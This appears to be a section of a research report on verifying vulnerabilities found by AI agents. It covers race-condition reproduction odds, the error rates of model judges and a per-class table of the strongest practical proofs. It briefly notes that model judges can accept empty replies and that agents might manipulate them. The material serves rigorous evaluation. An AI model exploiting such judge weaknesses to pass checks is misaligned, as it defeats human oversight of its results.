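In a race condition, a program goes wrong only when two events happen in an unlucky order. If each attempt triggers the race with probability *p*, the number of attempts needed for a 95% chance of seeing it is

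*n* = ln 0.05 / ln(1 − *p*) ≈ 3/*p*.

A race that succeeds once in 10,000 attempts needs about 30,000 attempts for a 95% chance of at least one success. AIxCC's default of 100 runs would reveal it only about 1% of the time.

A tester can insert a delay between the two steps to make the bad order happen every time. This proves that the program mishandles that order, but somebody still has to show that the order can occur without the delay. More work on the attack can also make an unreliable demonstration reliable. Cheng and colleagues report that public attacks on one V8 bug worked only some of the time, but Mythos Preview built one that almost always worked.

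A design may be weak even if the software always runs as intended. Suppose a company encrypts every customer's files with one key and keeps a copy of the key on each server. The encryption works correctly, but an intruder who takes over one server can read every customer's files. A tester could give an agent control of one server and ask it to retrieve a flag from a customer's files on another. Success would show what the design puts at risk if an intruder takes over a server. The company's engineers would still have to judge how likely that is and whether a redesign is worth the cost.

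An attack on a cipher can require less computation than the designers promised and still require far too much to run. The evidence is then a mathematical argument that experts or proof-checking software can verify, perhaps supported by a working attack on a smaller version of the cipher.

### Review by models and people

When a script can't settle a question, a second model or a person has to. Wang and colleagues measured how well models answer one narrow question, whether an attack that had captured a flag used the assigned bug. Two of the researchers independently labelled a sample of attacks, then resolved their disagreements. This left 58 usable cases, of which 30 used the assigned bug and 28 used another.

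| Judge | Correct, of 58 | Wrongly accepted, of 28 |
|---|---|---|
| Codex with GPT-5.5 | 58 | 0 |
| Claude Code with Claude Opus 4.6 | 56 | 2 |

These results are good, but the sample is small. A judge that wrongly accepted 10% of the unrelated attacks would still have about a 5% chance of judging all 28 correctly. The two judges agreed on 294 of 313 successful runs, and people decided the other 19. Only the Claude judge scored the runs of Mythos Preview and Opus 4.6. If it made mistakes at the rate in the table, about five of Mythos Preview's 157 successes used some other bug.

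The same error rate matters more when most claims are false. Let *π* be the share of claims that are true, *s* the share of true claims that a judge accepts and *f* the share of false claims that it accepts. The share of accepted claims that are true is

*πs* / (*πs* + (1 − *π*)*f*).

With *s* = 1 and *f* = 2/28, this is 93% if half the claims are true but only 61% if a tenth are. The real figure could be worse for unproven reports, because the judges in this experiment had a description of the bug and already knew that each attack had worked.

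Judges can also fail in simpler ways. In WebArena, a test of how well agents use websites, the model judge accepted an empty reply as correct on some tasks. *Establishing Best Practices for Building Rigorous Agentic Benchmarks* recommends measuring a judge's accuracy, consistency and agreement with people before relying on it, and checking that agents can't manipulate it.

Nobody measured the human error rate in these experiments, because the human labels served as the correct answers. The same is true of Anthropic's figure that reviewers confirmed 90.6% of its more serious findings. If two people judged each case independently, their labels would at least show how often they disagree. One attack in the original sample of 59 was left out because both experts were unsure about it.

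### The strongest proof for each class

The table below gives the most convincing proof that is usually practical for each class, and what people have to decide and supply.

| Vulnerability class | Strongest available proof | Human input needed |
|---|---|---|
| Memory error | An input that makes a sanitizer abort the real program, but not the fixed version | A realistic way for attackers to supply the input |
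| Command, SQL or code injection | A fresh flag recovered through the application's normal interface | The flag, and a statement of which input attackers control |
| Path traversal or server-side request forgery | The contents of a planted file or a private test server | A list of forbidden files and destinations |
| Cross-site scripting | The attacker's script running in a separate victim's browser | Roles and ordinary actions for attacker and victim |
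| Authorization bypass | One user reading or changing another's planted record | Test accounts, and a rule for who may do what |
| Logic flaw | A repeatable series of actions that breaks a stated rule | The rule |
| Theft from a smart contract | Funds gained in a simulation | A copy of the contract's state, and a definition of legitimate gains |
| Information leak | A planted secret recovered again after the tester changes it | A decision on what is secret, and from whom |
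| Timing side channel | A recovered key, or guesses that beat a threshold set in advance | The attacker's position, the hardware and the threshold |
| Wrong cryptographic result | A forged message that the library accepts, or a mismatch with a known answer | A trusted answer or a second implementation |
| Misuse of cryptography | A message decrypted or forged in the running application | A statement of what the encryption must protect |
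| Rare race | Repeated failures of the unmodified program, or one failure with an added delay | For the delayed version, an argument that the order can occur naturally |
| Weak design | A written argument, with a demonstration under stated assumptions | Expert judgment on whether the assumptions are realistic |
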